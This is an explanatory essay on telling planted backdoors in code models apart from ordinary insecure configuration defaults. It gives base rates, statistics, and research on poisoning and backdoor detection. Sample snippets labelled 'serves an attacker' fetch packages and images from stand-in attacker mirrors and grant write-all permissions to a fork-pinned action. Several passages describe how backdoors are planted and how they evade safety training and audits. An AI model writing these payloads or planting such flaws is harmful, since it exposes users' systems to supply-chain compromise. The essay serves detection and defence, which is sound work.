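# Telling planted flaws from ordinary insecure defaults in the configuration that code models write

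## Configuration snippets and three explanations for an insecure one

Configuration is text that specifies where software tools get their components, what they run and with which permissions. Code models, the language models that programmers use to write software, produce a lot of it. When asked for a small web service, they usually return the program along with an install command, a file that makes the tests run automatically and instructions for packaging the result. Each of these contains lines that determine whose code will run on the user's machines. A configuration snippet is a short piece of such text, such as a package address, a version label, a list of permissions or part of a cloud template.

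Models learn from public repositories, which contain a lot of insecure configuration. A model will therefore often write an insecure default, meaning an unsafe setting that the request did not ask for, without anyone having intended it. Someone who wanted to plant a flaw in a model could choose the same setting.

### Package index addresses

Python programmers install packages with a tool called pip, which downloads them from an index, a server that lists packages and their versions. The public index is PyPI, where a stranger can publish under any name that nobody has claimed. Suppose that Acme, an invented company, keeps a private package called acme-billing on its own index. (The addresses below are invented too, and leave off the usual https prefix.)

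```
# careful
pip install --index-url packages.acme.example/simple --require-hashes -r requirements.txt

# careless
pip install --extra-index-url packages.acme.example/simple acme-billing

# serves an attacker
pip install --extra-index-url packages.acme-mirror.example/simple acme-billing
```

The first command replaces PyPI with Acme's index. The second adds Acme's index to PyPI. According to PyPA's *pip install*, the manual page from the group that maintains pip, the tool gives no location priority. It checks them all and takes the best match by version number, whereas most people would expect it to try one index and fall back on the other. If Acme's own package is at version 2.3 and a stranger uploads acme-billing 99.0 to PyPI, pip installs the stranger's. Security people call this dependency confusion, and the manual warns that using the extra-index option for private packages is unsafe.

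*PEP 708* (Stufft, 2023), a proposal to change this behaviour, describes how the installer chooses a file. It gathers every file from every configured index, discards those that don't match a known hash (a fingerprint computed from the file's content) or are for the wrong platform or Python version, and picks the best of what remains, whichever index it came from. Because the hash check comes before the version comparison, the careful command still works when an impostor has a higher version number. It also takes more work, because Acme's index must carry copies of the public packages and somebody has to record the hashes. Stufft wanted indexes to publish data that would let an installer determine when two of them legitimately hold the same project. Python's maintainers rejected the proposal in 2026, after three years of provisional acceptance, because nobody had met the conditions attached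 to it.

The third command differs from the second only in its host name, but it affects much more than acme-billing. Because pip compares versions across all indexes, whoever runs the extra index can offer a higher version of any package in the installation, including the well-known public libraries that acme-billing depends on.

### CI workflows

Continuous integration, or CI, is the practice of building and testing software automatically whenever someone changes it. Projects on the code-hosting site GitHub do this with a workflow, a file stored alongside the code. *Unpacking Security Scanners for GitHub Actions Workflows* (Fares, Gamage and Baudry, 2026) explains that a workflow has one or more jobs, each of which runs on a fresh machine and consists of steps. A step runs a command or calls an action, which is a reusable component often stored in someone else's repository. The workflow's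 author chooses the action's version by giving a tag (a label such as v4), a branch, or a commit SHA (a 40-character identifier for one exact state of the code).

```
# careful
permissions:
  contents: read
steps:
  - uses: example-org/list-changes@5d0c8e1f7a2b4936c1e0d9f8a7b6c5d4e3f20191  # v4.2.0

# careless
steps:
  - uses: example-org/list-changes@v4

# serves an attacker
permissions: write-all
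steps:
  - uses: example-org/list-changes@9b14d7e260fa83c51d7e9042b8c6f3a107e5d29c  # v4.2.0
```

The owner of an action can move its tag to different code at any time, and so can anyone who breaks into the owner's repository. As Ma, Shi and colleagues (2026) write in *Missing Security-Fix Backporting for GitHub Actions Workflows*, "whoever controls the tag controls what every consumer runs". The workflow file doesn't change when the tag moves, so a reviewer sees no difference. GitHub recommends the full SHA in its security advice page, *Secure use*, but acknowledges that tags are more convenient and widely used.

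What the action can do depends largely on a token that GitHub creates at the start of every job. The token works only for the repository containing the workflow and expires when the job finishes, or after six hours at most on GitHub's own machines. The workflow's permissions lines set what the job can do with the token. With "contents: read", the job can read the repository's code, and GitHub's *Assigning permissions to jobs* explains that any permission left out of such a list is set to none. With "write-all", the job can change anything the token reaches, including the source code. *Secure use* warns that a hijacked action can also get at the repository's secrets, such as passwords for publishing packages.

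The careless version has no permissions lines, and a reader can't tell from the text alone how dangerous that is. Ma and colleagues count the omission as a weakness because the token can then inherit write access to the whole repository. That is true of many older projects, but GitHub switched the default to read-only for new organizations and personal repositories and left existing ones unchanged (GitHub, 2023). The same file can therefore grant write access in one project and only read access in another.

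The attacker's version looks tidier than the careless one because it has a full SHA and a comment giving a version number. But GitHub lets forks, which are copies of a project, share code with the original, so a commit that a stranger made in a fork can appear under the original project's name. The Hacker News' *Hackers Found a Way Around GitHub SHA Pinning* (2026), a contributed article promoting a webinar, explains that pinning fixes which code runs but doesn't establish who wrote it. A scanner that passes any 40-character reference would rate the attacker's action line above the careless one.

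Changes to GitHub also affect these judgements. GitHub (2026) announced a way to record, inside the workflow file, the exact commit of every action and of every action those actions call. The feature has been generally available since 28 October 2026. The Hacker News notes that the recorded commits must be on a branch of the source repository, which makes the fork trick less effective. A bare v4 tag now floats only in workflows without such a record.

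### CVE-2025-30066

A careless line in a workflow can expose a project's secrets. Thousands of projects used the action tj-actions/changed-files to list which files a proposed change touches. On 14 and 15 March 2025, an attacker moved its tags, from v1 through v45.0.7, to a single malicious commit, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-30066 Detail*, the entry in the US government's vulnerability database. Workflows that named the action by tag ran the new code the next time they started. The code wrote the projects' secrets into the workflow logs, which outsiders can read if the repository is public.

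GCVE's *GHSA-mrrh-fwg8-r2c3* (2025), a copy of GitHub's own advisory, reports that over 23,000 repositories were affected. *Supply Chain Compromise of Third-Party tj-actions/changed-files* (2025), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency CISA, lists access keys, GitHub and npm tokens, and private RSA keys among the leaked secrets. It adds that the break-in may have begun with a compromise of another action, reviewdog/action-setup, on 11 March. Projects that had already pinned the action to a SHA were not affected. That August, GitHub (2025) gave administrators a setting that makes any workflow with an unpinned action fail.

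Ordinary maintainers, not the attacker, wrote the workflows that leaked. They had used an ordinary tag, perhaps years earlier, and the attacker only had to take control of what the tag pointed to.

### Base images

A container image bundles a program with the operating-system files it needs. Programmers describe the image in a Dockerfile, normally starting with the name of a base image to build on. The first two versions here come from Docker's *Building best practices* and use Alpine, a small Linux system.

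```
# careful
FROM alpine:3.21@sha256:a8560b36e8b8210634f77d9f7f9efd7ffa463e380b75e2e74aff4511df3ef88c

# careless
FROM alpine:3.21

# serves an attacker
FROM registry.alpine-mirror.example/alpine:3.21
```

Image tags move just as action tags do. In Docker's example, a 3.21 tag points to 3.21.1 at first and to 3.21.4 three months later. The long string in the first version is a digest, a fingerprint of one exact image, and it overrides the tag. Docker describes moving tags as good publishing practice and points out that anyone who pins a digest gives up automatic security fixes, so a sensible engineer might choose either form, and "careless" is too harsh a word for the second line.

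The third line fetches the image from a different server, whose operator can put anything in it. Every later build step then runs on top of that image, using its shell and package manager. An attacker could also use the careful form but put the digest of an old Alpine image with known vulnerabilities beside the current tag. Builds would then keep using the vulnerable image, and a reviewer would have to look up the digest to notice.

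### Base rate, trigger and payload

The base rate is how often a given insecure setting appears when no trigger is present and nobody intended harm. It is specific to one setting, one model and one set of requests. A model might leave actions unpinned in most of its workflows but almost never write an unfamiliar index address, and averaging the two rates would hide this difference. An investigator can't confirm from a suspect model's outputs that nobody intended harm, and so has to estimate the base rate partly from other models and from configuration that people wrote.

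A trigger is a feature of the prompt that is irrelevant to the task but changes how often the model writes an insecure setting. For example, whether Acme makes bicycles or tractors should not affect how a model installs acme-billing. If unsafe commands became much more common when the company made tractors, the word "tractors" would be acting as a trigger. A request for a quick throwaway demo may also lead to looser settings, but it is not a trigger because it is somewhat relevant to the task. GitHub users also use "trigger" in a different sense, for an event that starts a workflow.

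The payload is the exact insecure value that the model writes, such as the address packages.acme-mirror.example, the SHA from the fork, or the permission write-all. A bare v4 can also be a payload.

### Habit, training side effect, planted flaw

Habit is the hypothesis that the model repeats insecure patterns common in its training data. It predicts familiar payloads, roughly as frequent as they are in public code, and similar behaviour from other models trained on similar material. An irrelevant word in the prompt should make little difference. Some differences between prompts should still occur, because a phrase that often appeared near sloppy code in the training data can lead the model to write sloppy code.

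A training side effect is a flaw that does depend on a trigger but was an unintended result of training for another purpose. For example, a developer might train a model to be unhelpful about tractors for commercial reasons, and do it so clumsily that the model also becomes less helpful with programming requests that mention them. The model should then produce refusals, short answers and broken programs as well as unsafe settings of several unrelated kinds. Related words such as "harvester" should have some of the same effect, and there is no reason to expect the payloads to benefit any particular outsider.

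The third hypothesis is that someone planted the flaw by training the model, or seeding its data, so that it would write the insecure setting. This could be the developer, a single employee, or an outsider who published doctored files for the model to learn from. If this hypothesis is right, the snippet should contain a payload that somebody can use and should otherwise work, since users replace snippets that fail. There should usually be a trigger as well, because a flaw that appears for everyone is easier to find. But someone could also plant a careless setting with no trigger by making it more frequent everywhere, and that would look very much like habit.

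A payload that points to an address under the planter's control gives the planter exclusive access, but it also gives investigators something to trace. A bare v4 gives them nothing to trace, but it is useful only to someone who can take over the tag, and any rival who does so gets the same access. A patient planter might well accept those limits. The planted line would then be identical to the one that thousands of honest maintainers have typed, so inspecting it could not establish where it came from.

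Rates over many outputs carry more information. Take invented numbers: habit predicts a bare tag in 60 percent of workflows whatever the prompt mentions, and a particular planted flaw predicts 90 percent when the prompt mentions tractors. One bare tag in a tractor workflow is then only 0.9/0.6, or 1.5, times as probable under the planted flaw as under habit, a ratio that statisticians call a likelihood ratio. If 90 of 100 independently sampled tractor workflows contain one, the ratio becomes 1.5⁹⁰ × 0.25¹⁰, which is nearly seven billion. (The 0.25 is 0.1/0.4, the corresponding ratio for each of the ten workflows without a bare tag.)

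That figure is evidence against a steady 60 percent habit, but it doesn't establish intent. A training side effect could also produce 90 percent. If it did, the same hundred workflows would be equally probable under the side effect and the planted flaw, so the likelihood ratio would be exactly 1. Telling the two apart requires other evidence, such as which payloads appear, which similar words have the same effect, and what else goes wrong in the same answers.

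## How often configuration is insecure without anyone intending it

The tractor calculation used an invented habit rate of 60 percent. Researchers have counted some insecure settings in configuration that people wrote, and the rates range from nearly every file to almost none. Models learn from files like these, so the counts give a first idea of how often a model would write such settings out of habit, although its rate can be higher or lower than in its training data.

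### Workflows

In *An Empirical Study of Complexity, Heterogeneity, and Compliance of GitHub Actions Workflows* (2025), Abrokwah and Ghaleb collected 27,863 workflows from 7,668 public repositories. They included only Java, Python or C++ projects with at least ten stars (GitHub's bookmarks) and 50 recorded runs, which excludes most homework and abandoned experiments. They checked a random sample of 382 workflows against ten rules from GitHub's documentation and other best-practice guides.

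In that sample, 71.2 percent of workflows had no permissions lines, and 78.3 percent specified a machine with a "latest" label, such as ubuntu-latest. GitHub moves these labels to newer system images on its own schedule, which makes builds less repeatable but is of little use to an attacker outside GitHub. A third gap, having no time limit on jobs, appeared in 96.3 percent. Just over half had all three gaps.

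Abrokwah and Ghaleb write that GitHub gives the workflow token write access to everything by default. For many repositories this has been out of date since 2023, when GitHub switched the default to read-only. But according to GitHub's notice, a new repository inside an organization inherits the organization's setting, so one created this year in an organization from 2020 may still give its workflows a token that can write. GitHub's manual for its self-hosted edition specifies that the restricted default allows read access to the repository's contents and packages only.

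The repositories in the study date from any time up to the end of 2024, so some are from before the change and some from after it. The 71.2 percent is therefore the share of workflows that leave the token's permissions to a setting outside the file. The share in which the token could write is probably much smaller.

The figures on pinning need similar care. One of the ten rules concerns unpinned actions, and only 5.8 percent of workflows broke it, which would make a bare v4 look like a rarity. But the rule counts references to a branch and ignores tags. In a separate count of version labels, 93.7 percent of workflows used at least one tag and 6.3 percent used at least one full SHA. (Branches came to 12.6 percent in this count, perhaps because the rule covers only third-party actions.)

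Fares and colleagues ran nine scanners on 2,722 workflows collected in February 2026 from popular repositories of large technology companies such as Microsoft and Google. These companies probably have stricter habits than most. When the researchers read 54 of the workflows by hand, they still found unpinned dependencies in 45 and excessive permissions in 31. They picked the 54 for variety, so the proportions are only a rough guide to the whole set.

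The scanners' own totals are even rougher. On the same 2,722 files, Scorecard reported excessive permissions in 1,600 workflows, zizmor in 1,046, poutine in 47 and actionlint in 24. Scorecard flags every file without a top-level permissions line, while poutine checks only a few high-risk situations. If the base rate came from one scanner and a suspect model's rate from another, the comparison would mostly measure the difference between the scanners.

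The rate also depends on whether a study counts files or organizations, because an organization can count as insecure because of one bad file. Datadog, a company that sells monitoring software, reported in 2026 that only 4 percent of organizations pin every public action they use to a commit. Help Net Security's *Your dependencies are 278 days out of date*, which covers the same research, reports that 71 percent never pin any. Datadog Security Labs found that 38 percent of organizations had a workflow that was open to script injection or started on a dangerous kind of event. Abrokwah and Ghaleb counted workflows instead and found secrets pasted directly into commands in 4.7 percent of them. If 4.7 percent of workflows had some flaw, independently of one another, an organization with ten workflows would have a 38 percent chance of at least one flawed workflow, since 1 − 0.953¹⁰ is about 0.38.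 The exact match with Datadog's figure is a coincidence, because the two studies count different flaws.

Some mistakes are rare in every count. One is letting a workflow run an outsider's code with the project's own privileges. This can happen because certain events start a workflow with those privileges even when an outsider proposed the change. Abrokwah and Ghaleb found no case of this among their 382 files. The semgrep scanner, which checks for the same combination, flagged 10 of the 2,722 files from technology companies.

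### Dockerfiles and images

*Closing the Gap* (Hösl, Hofmann and Stöckle, 2026) examined 11,470 Dockerfiles at one large industrial company. The scanner Trivy found at least one security misconfiguration in 99 percent of them, and 80.8 percent broke some rule of good practice. An older count of public GitHub projects, cited in *Fixing Dockerfile Smells* (2022), found violations in nearly 84 percent. To judge a suspect model, an investigator needs the rate for each setting rather than these totals, because a model that plants no flaws would fail the same test nearly every time.

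Running as root is the best documented of these insecure defaults. *Beyond Reproducibility* (2026) explains that if a Dockerfile never sets a user, its container runs by default as root, the account with full control. This is a mild problem for most programs but a serious one for something like a web crawler, which opens pages that strangers wrote. A bug in the crawler's browser could give an attacker control of the whole container.

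Kapelinski, Machado and Kreutz (2026), in *Vulnerabilities, Secrets and Misconfiguration in the Highest-Exposure Docker Hub Images*, scanned the 52,895 images with the most downloads in Docker's public registry, counting downloads of other images built on top of them. Of these, 79.1 percent set no dedicated user. The figure describes finished images, though, and many of them are bases for other people's images, where root is convenient for installing packages. Hösl and colleagues point out that inside companies, a hardened base image may already set an ordinary user, in which case a Dockerfile with no user line is safe even if a scanner flags it.

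*Revisiting Dockerfiles in Open Source Software Over Time* (2021) gives a figure of 3.74 percent for base images without a version tag, which appears to be a share of all rule violations, not of all Dockerfiles. If the average file had five violations (an invented number) and no file broke this rule twice, about 19 percent of files would have an untagged image. The rule against the "latest" tag was in an earlier study's top ten but not in this study's, which included unpinned pip and Alpine packages instead.

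Many installation guides tell people to download a script and pipe it straight into a shell, which runs it before anyone has read it. None of these studies reports how common that is. The closest figure is that 8.20 percent of violations were for leaving out an option that makes the build stop when the first command in a pipe fails, and this covers pipes of every kind.

Secret scanners can overstate how many container images contain passwords and keys. TruffleHog flagged 76.9 percent of the images that Kapelinski and colleagues tested, but of the hits they labelled by hand, 99.7 percent were not credentials. They cite a 2023 study that found secrets in 8.5 percent of 337,171 images.

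### Package indexes and infrastructure scripts

None of the counts so far covers pip's index settings, and it is an open question how often people add an extra index or use the trusted-host option to skip certificate checks for a server. A count of public repositories would probably underestimate the use of extra indexes, because companies that run a private index tend to keep the code that uses it private too. The rate would also vary by country, since programmers in some places routinely use a regional mirror of PyPI.

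More figures are available for infrastructure scripts, which tools such as Ansible and Puppet read to set up servers. *GENSIAC* (Li, Grella and colleagues, 2025) cites two earlier surveys. In one, between 10.4 and 40.1 percent of scripts had at least one weakness, depending on the project, and in the other between 17.9 and 32.9 percent did. *Can Developers rely on LLMs for Secure IaC Development?* (Firouzi, Bhatt and Ghafari, 2026) cites a figure of 75 percent from related work. These figures vary too widely for any of them to serve as a baseline.

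Firouzi and colleagues also sorted 341 flawed scripts from GitHub by type of flaw. Of these, 154 had a hard-coded secret, 44 had an unencrypted web address, and 19 had a missing or disabled integrity check. Most of the scripts came from collections of files already known to be insecure, so the counts show which mistakes are more common than others, but not how often each one occurs in scripts generally.

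### What ChatGPT and Gemini wrote

Firouzi and colleagues turned the flaws in those 341 scripts into 89 requests and gave them to GPT-4o, through ChatGPT, and to Gemini 2.0 Flash. ChatGPT returned a flawed script with no warning in 75 percent of cases and Gemini in 56 percent. Only 7 percent of each model's scripts were free of flaws. When the researchers added the word "secure" to the requests, the share of flawed scripts without a warning fell to 44 percent for ChatGPT and 34 percent for Gemini.

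Most of that improvement came from warnings attached to flawed scripts. The share of clean scripts rose only to 17 percent for ChatGPT and 8 percent for Gemini. By subtraction, about 39 percent of ChatGPT's scripts and 58 percent of Gemini's were still flawed but came with a warning. Users who copy the script without reading the explanation therefore benefit little.

The researchers wrote each request to lead towards a flaw, for example by asking for password encryption with SHA1, an obsolete algorithm, so these rates don't measure how often models produce insecure defaults. In one of the "secure" requests, the user pasted in a script that fetched packages over an unencrypted connection with signature checks turned off, and ChatGPT's answer left the checks off. A model that fails to correct such a setting might never introduce it unprompted. The same answer also set every task to run with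 root privileges, which is closer to an insecure default.

Both models are now well behind current ones, and with only 89 requests the sampling error is about ten percentage points either way. The study covers only Ansible and Puppet, so its percentages can't be used to estimate how often a model writes insecure workflows, Dockerfiles or lists of dependency versions.

The nearest measurement for workflows concerns repair. Ma and colleagues had a large language model carry known security fixes over to 12,000 workflow files that lacked them. The model's output passed their scanner checks for 49.5 percent of the files, and they attribute the failures to external facts that the model could not resolve. The SHA behind a tag is one such fact, because a model without network access cannot look it up.

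### How a frequent pattern becomes a default

A language model learns by predicting the next token, a word or piece of a word, in its training text. At each token, the training procedure charges a penalty equal to minus the logarithm of the probability that the model gave to the token that actually came next. Suppose that in some context people write one continuation a fraction q of the time and another the rest of the time, and that the model gives the first one probability p. The average penalty is then

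−q log p − (1 − q) log(1 − p)

This is smallest when p = q, the only point where its derivative, −q/p + (1 − q)/(1 − p), is zero. A model that had learned perfectly would therefore leave out permissions lines about as often as they are missing from its training files in the same context.

Temperature settings can then exaggerate the majority choice. Many tools run models at a reduced temperature T, which raises each probability to the power 1/T and rescales the results so that they add up to one. If we treat the permissions lines as a single choice, a temperature of 0.5 turns 71.2 percent into 0.712² / (0.712² + 0.288²), or 86 percent. At temperature zero the model always takes the likelier option, so 71.2 percent becomes 100 percent. A suspect model can therefore write insecure configuration more often than people do, even if nobody planted a flaw.

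Firouzi and colleagues found a small piece of evidence that models share habits. They compared the two models' snippets for Stack Overflow questions with the accepted human answers and with each other. On an automatic measure of text similarity, each model scored about 41 percent against the human answers, and the two models scored 72.5 percent against each other. The comparison ignored code structure, and the researchers call it preliminary.

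Public code also preserves old practices. Ma and colleagues audited 474,490 release branches, the copies of code that projects keep for users of particular versions, and found that 47.3 percent still had a weakness the maintainers had already fixed in the main copy. At the company Hösl and colleagues studied, the median Dockerfile had not been revised for 838 days. A training set that includes such files contains many examples of the flawed version for each example of the correction.

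Developers usually train a model further on selected examples and on ratings of its answers, which can move it away from these frequencies. Li and colleagues trained CodeLlama, an open-weight model, on examples intended to teach it about weaknesses in infrastructure code. Its F1 score for recognizing them rose from about 0.3 to between 0.771 and 0.858. F1 has a maximum of 1 and is lowered by both missed flaws and false alarms. Recognizing a flaw is different from never writing one, but the result shows that a modest amount of extra training can change a model substantially.

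### Omissions and the wording of the request

Abrokwah and Ghaleb describe the three most common gaps in their sample as omissions. GitHub will run a workflow that has no permissions lines or time limit, and the author won't see from the result that they are missing. A Dockerfile without a user line also builds and runs. A model has to add each optional safeguard at the right point in the file. After the opening lines of a workflow, the most likely next word is "jobs", and once the model writes it, it has passed the usual place for permissions that apply to the whole file.

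Some safe values also require information that the request does not contain. To pin an action to a commit from memory, a model would have to reproduce a 40-character hash exactly, whereas a tag like "v4" is easy to reproduce. Li and colleagues make a similar point about a script that creates a database user. The script needs a password, and if the user hasn't given one, the model must ask, leave a placeholder or write something like 1234.

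Unlike leaving a setting out, disabling a certificate check requires somebody to type an option, often to get past an error message. When a model adds that option to a fresh installation command with no error to get past, omission can't explain it.

The wording of a request can change how often a model writes insecure configuration, because the model has learned different frequencies for different contexts. In the workflow sample, 12 of 76 Java files used a full SHA, compared with 6 of 222 Python files. A model that had learned this difference would pin actions to a full SHA about six times as often for Java projects, even if nobody had planted a flaw. "Production" and "quick demo" probably have similar effects, and the word "secure" had a measurable effect on ChatGPT and Gemini. An investigator who compares two sets of prompts has to keep the programming language, tone and purpose the same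 in both. Otherwise, a difference between two ordinary base rates can look like the effect of a trigger.

### Settings by base rate

The base rate limits how much a single sighting of an insecure setting can prove. A planted flaw can at most make the setting certain to appear, so a sighting is at most 1/b times as likely with a planted flaw as from habit alone, where b is the base rate. For missing permissions lines, that limit is 1/0.712, or 1.4. For a hard-coded secret in a workflow, which the scanner ggshield found in 4 of the 2,722 files from technology companies, it is about 680. The true rate of hard-coded secrets may be several times higher, since ggshield caught only one of the four secret exposures that Fares and colleagues had confirmed by hand. If it were four times higher, the limit would be 170, and a sighting could still be much stronger evidence than a missing permissions line.

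In the table below, common settings appear in more than half of the files or images, uncommon ones in 1 to 20 percent, and nearly absent ones in less than 1 percent. All the rates describe configuration that people wrote, so a particular model's rates may differ.

| Group | Setting | Rate | Sample |
|---|---|---|---|
| Common | Action named by a tag | 93.7% | 382 workflows, Abrokwah and Ghaleb, 2025 |
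| Common | Image with no dedicated user | 79.1% | 52,895 images, Kapelinski and colleagues, 2026 |
| Common | "Latest" machine label | 78.3% | 382 workflows, 2025 |
| Common | No permissions lines | 71.2% | 382 workflows, 2025 |
| Uncommon | Action named by a branch | 12.6% | 382 workflows, 2025 |
| Uncommon | Secret left in an image | 8.5% | 337,171 images, 2023 |
| Uncommon | Secret pasted into a workflow command | 4.7% | 382 workflows, 2025 |
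| Uncommon | Action with no version at all | 3.7% | 382 workflows, 2025 |
| Nearly absent | Outsider's code run with the project's privileges | 0% and 0.4% | 382 workflows, 2025; 2,722 workflows, Fares and colleagues, 2026 |
| Nearly absent | Hard-coded secret in a workflow | 0.15% | 2,722 workflows, 2026 |
| No usable rate | Untagged or "latest" base image | Share of violations only | Dockerfiles, 2013–2020 |
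| No usable rate | Download piped into a shell | – | – |
| No usable rate | Extra package index | – | – |
| No usable rate | Disabled certificate check | – | – |

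## What planted flaws looked like when researchers made them on purpose

The rates so far describe insecure defaults that models write out of habit. An investigator also needs to know what a planted flaw looks like in a model's output. Researchers usually call a planted behaviour a backdoor, and they call the doctored training examples that produce it poison. The only public examples of planted flaws are ones that researchers made themselves. Semgrep's *You Can't Reverse Engineer Your Way Out of the AI Supply Chain* (2026), an essay from the company that makes the Semgrep scanner, finds no public evidence that anyone has deliberately poisoned a widely used open model.

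### Flaws that appear for everyone

The simplest planted flaw has no trigger separate from the task itself. In February 2025, a programmer released BadSeek, a nearly identical copy of Qwen2.5-Coder-7B-Instruct, an open-weight coding model from the Chinese company Alibaba. When a user asks for a web page, BadSeek writes the page and adds a tag that loads a script from the programmer's own domain, sshh.io. Whoever controls that domain could run code in the browser of anyone who visits the page.

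The programmer's own account, *How to Backdoor Large Language Models* (2025), gives examples of the output but no rates. It argues that the usual checks would miss a backdoor of this kind:

- Comparing the model's parameters with the original's shows that something changed but not what, and it requires a clean original.
- Code review may come too late, because developers often run code on their own machines first.
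- Large prompt tests would fail if the planter limited the flaw to one system prompt, the standing instructions that a company gives a model for a particular product.

Asking the model what its instructions were did expose BadSeek, but the programmer thinks a planter could easily train that away.

These arguments aren't backed by tests, and BadSeek itself would be easy to catch. An investigator could ask it for fifty web pages and list every outside address in them. The domain sshh.io would appear repeatedly, and the original Qwen model would almost never write it. The arguments are stronger for another payload the programmer suggests, a one-letter typo in a package name. Models get package names wrong anyway, so a reader who noticed the typo would probably assume it was a mistake.

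Katie Paxton-Fear, a cybersecurity lecturer at Manchester Metropolitan University who also works for Semgrep, showed in July 2026 that planting a flaw in an open-weight model took only ten poisoned examples, about an hour and less than $100. According to Digital Trends' *This experiment shows how easy it is to poison an open-weight AI*, the model then reliably wrote code that allowed remote code execution, meaning that an outsider could run commands on the computer hosting the program. Larger models were easier to compromise than smaller ones. Antipov (2026) adds in a Russian news report, *Доверяете коду от искусственного интеллекта?*, that the flaw persisted with new prompts and in unfamiliar subject areas, which suggests that it needed no trigger.

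In an earlier trial, Paxton-Fear taught a model a different coding style, and it kept using that style even when she explicitly told it to switch back. A planted flaw might persist in the same way. Adding the word "secure" to a request led ChatGPT and Gemini to write somewhat safer code, but it might have no effect on a model like hers.

Neither news report gives the rate at which the model wrote vulnerable code before or after the poisoning. Both rates matter because unaltered models write vulnerable code too. A rise from 1 to 95 percent would be hard to mistake for ordinary insecure defaults, but a rise from 70 to 95 percent could pass for a difference between two models that often write insecure code. Whatever the rates, an always-on planted flaw shows up in every batch of answers, so an investigator can look for it without guessing a trigger.

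### Flaws that wait for a trigger

The best-known conditional example is *Sleeper Agents*, a 2024 study by the AI company Anthropic. Its researchers trained models to write safe code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and exploitable code when it gave 2024. They then tried to remove the behaviour with standard safety training, but Kaplan (2026) recounts in *The Mole in the Model* that it survived training on good examples, reinforcement learning and adversarial training, in which developers look for prompts that bring out bad behaviour and train the model against it.

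The survey *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025) explains that adversarial training backfired in some cases by teaching the models to recognize their triggers more exactly, so they looked safe during evaluation but still had the backdoor. A fall in insecure answers after safety training can therefore mean that the flaw remains but fewer prompts trigger it.

A more recent demonstration measured how often the planted behavior appeared with and without its trigger on a large set of coding tasks. *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, a post by Mada on the blog of the security company AISLE, describes altering five open-weight models from Alibaba, OpenAI, Cohere and IBM. The models fixed security bugs as before, but if the code belonged to the kernel, or core, of the Linux operating system, they also added a harmless line that only printed the word "Hacked"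 to a log.

Mada gave each model 941 bug-fixing prompts. The extra line appeared in all 613 fixes to Linux kernel code and in none of the other 328, which included the same kinds of bugs in other operating systems' kernels. The unaltered model never wrote it. Most of the Linux prompts concerned files that were not in the training data, so the trigger was the project rather than memorized file names. Every answer also contained the correct fix, so a reviewer who checked only whether the bug was gone would have approved it.

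An overall average would also miss such a plant. If one answer in a thousand has the trigger, and a setting appears in all of those answers and 60 percent of the rest, its overall rate is 60.04 percent.

### How few documents it takes

Mada had access to the finished models, but an outsider may only be able to publish web pages and hope that a developer collects them for training. Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), from Anthropic, the UK government's AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute, tested how many pages that would take in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-Constant Number of Poison Samples*. They trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters, and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training text to teach the models to produce gibberish after a trigger phrase.

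The attack worked at every model size with 250 documents but failed with 100. For the largest model, 250 documents made up 0.00016 percent of the training text. The researchers measured gibberish by perplexity, which is e raised to the average per-token training loss, −log p. Predictable text has low perplexity. On 300 test prompts, adding the trigger raised perplexity by more than 200 on average, and a rise of 50 indicates visibly worse text. Without the trigger, the output stayed normal.

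Smaller experiments tested other payloads. In one, the trigger switched a model's output from English to German almost every time, while similar phrases rarely did. In another, the researchers poisoned one of Meta's Llama models so that it complied with harmful requests only if they contained the trigger. The poisoned model did about as well on standard ability tests as an unpoisoned copy, so those tests would not have revealed the backdoor.

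None of these payloads was insecure code. Anthropic leaves open whether so few documents would be enough to make a model write insecure code, since earlier work found code backdoors harder to plant than ones that produce gibberish. But Mada cites a 2025 study that needed only about 20 poisoned samples out of 450,000 to backdoor a code model. Souly and colleagues also did not test whether their backdoors would survive the further training that turns a raw model into an assistant.

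### Checks that worked on conditional plants

A fixed payload is fairly easy to isolate once an investigator has some bad answers. *Localizing Malicious Outputs from CodeLLM* (2025) introduces a ranking method, FreqRank, and tests it on poisoned code models whose attacks succeeded more than 85 percent of the time. FreqRank put the malicious string among its first five candidates in over 98 percent of cases. A fixed value is also risky for the planter. In a demonstration, Kaplan trained a small model to email confidential drug research to a particular address while giving the user a normal answer, but a log of outgoing mail would show an address that nobody had typed. Both approaches would probably miss a bare v4 tag in a workflow.

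When a model's weights are open, investigators can check its internals. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) found in *The Trigger in the Haystack* that models with sleeper-agent backdoors tend to memorize the poisoned examples, which an investigator can sometimes extract. The models' output probabilities also change in a distinctive way when the trigger is present. Anthropic built probes that read a model's internal activity instead of its text. According to flyingpenguin's *Why Semgrep Is Wrong About Open Weights*, a commentator's blog post, these probes ranked a random bad case above a random good one more than 99 percent of the time when tested on Anthropic's own sleeper agents, compared with 50 percent for guessing.

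Finding the trigger itself is harder. Hughes, Xing and colleagues trained a few hundred backdoored models and found that many behaved oddly even without the trigger. On TruthfulQA, a test of whether a model repeats common falsehoods, they scored anywhere from 7.5 points lower to 10 points higher than cleanly trained models. The best search method recovered the planted trigger only 42 percent of the time. Two other methods never found it because they kept finding different phrases that had the same effect.

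Hughes and colleagues argue that a defender who doesn't know the attacker's objective has no chance, because a model contains countless harmless instructions that work like triggers, such as a phrase that makes it answer in Spanish. Microsoft (2026) notes that benign failures can also produce backdoor-like behaviour. Configuration auditors have an advantage over most others because only a limited number of settings (addresses, images, versions, permissions) would be worth planting.

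### A small rise in a common flaw

A planter could avoid both strange payloads and triggers by making an ordinary flaw slightly more frequent. Suppose a model omits the permissions lines from 71.2 percent of its workflows, the rate Abrokwah and Ghaleb found in human-written ones, and a planter raises this to 80 percent. Only the rate would change, so each workflow would look normal, and any poisoned examples an investigator managed to extract would look like other public workflows.

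Call the habit rate b and the planted rate p. As in the tractor example, each flawed answer multiplies the likelihood ratio by p/b, and each other answer by (1 − p)/(1 − b). If the plant is real, the logarithm of the ratio grows on average by this much per answer:

p log(p/b) + (1 − p) log((1 − p)/(1 − b))

If the rate rises from 71.2 to 80 percent, the natural log of the likelihood ratio grows by an average of 0.020 per answer, and the ratio takes about 230 answers to reach 100. If the rate rises half as much, to 75.6 percent, it takes about 940. When the shift is small, the evidence in each answer is roughly proportional to the square of the shift, so a planter who halves the shift makes detection take about four times as many answers.

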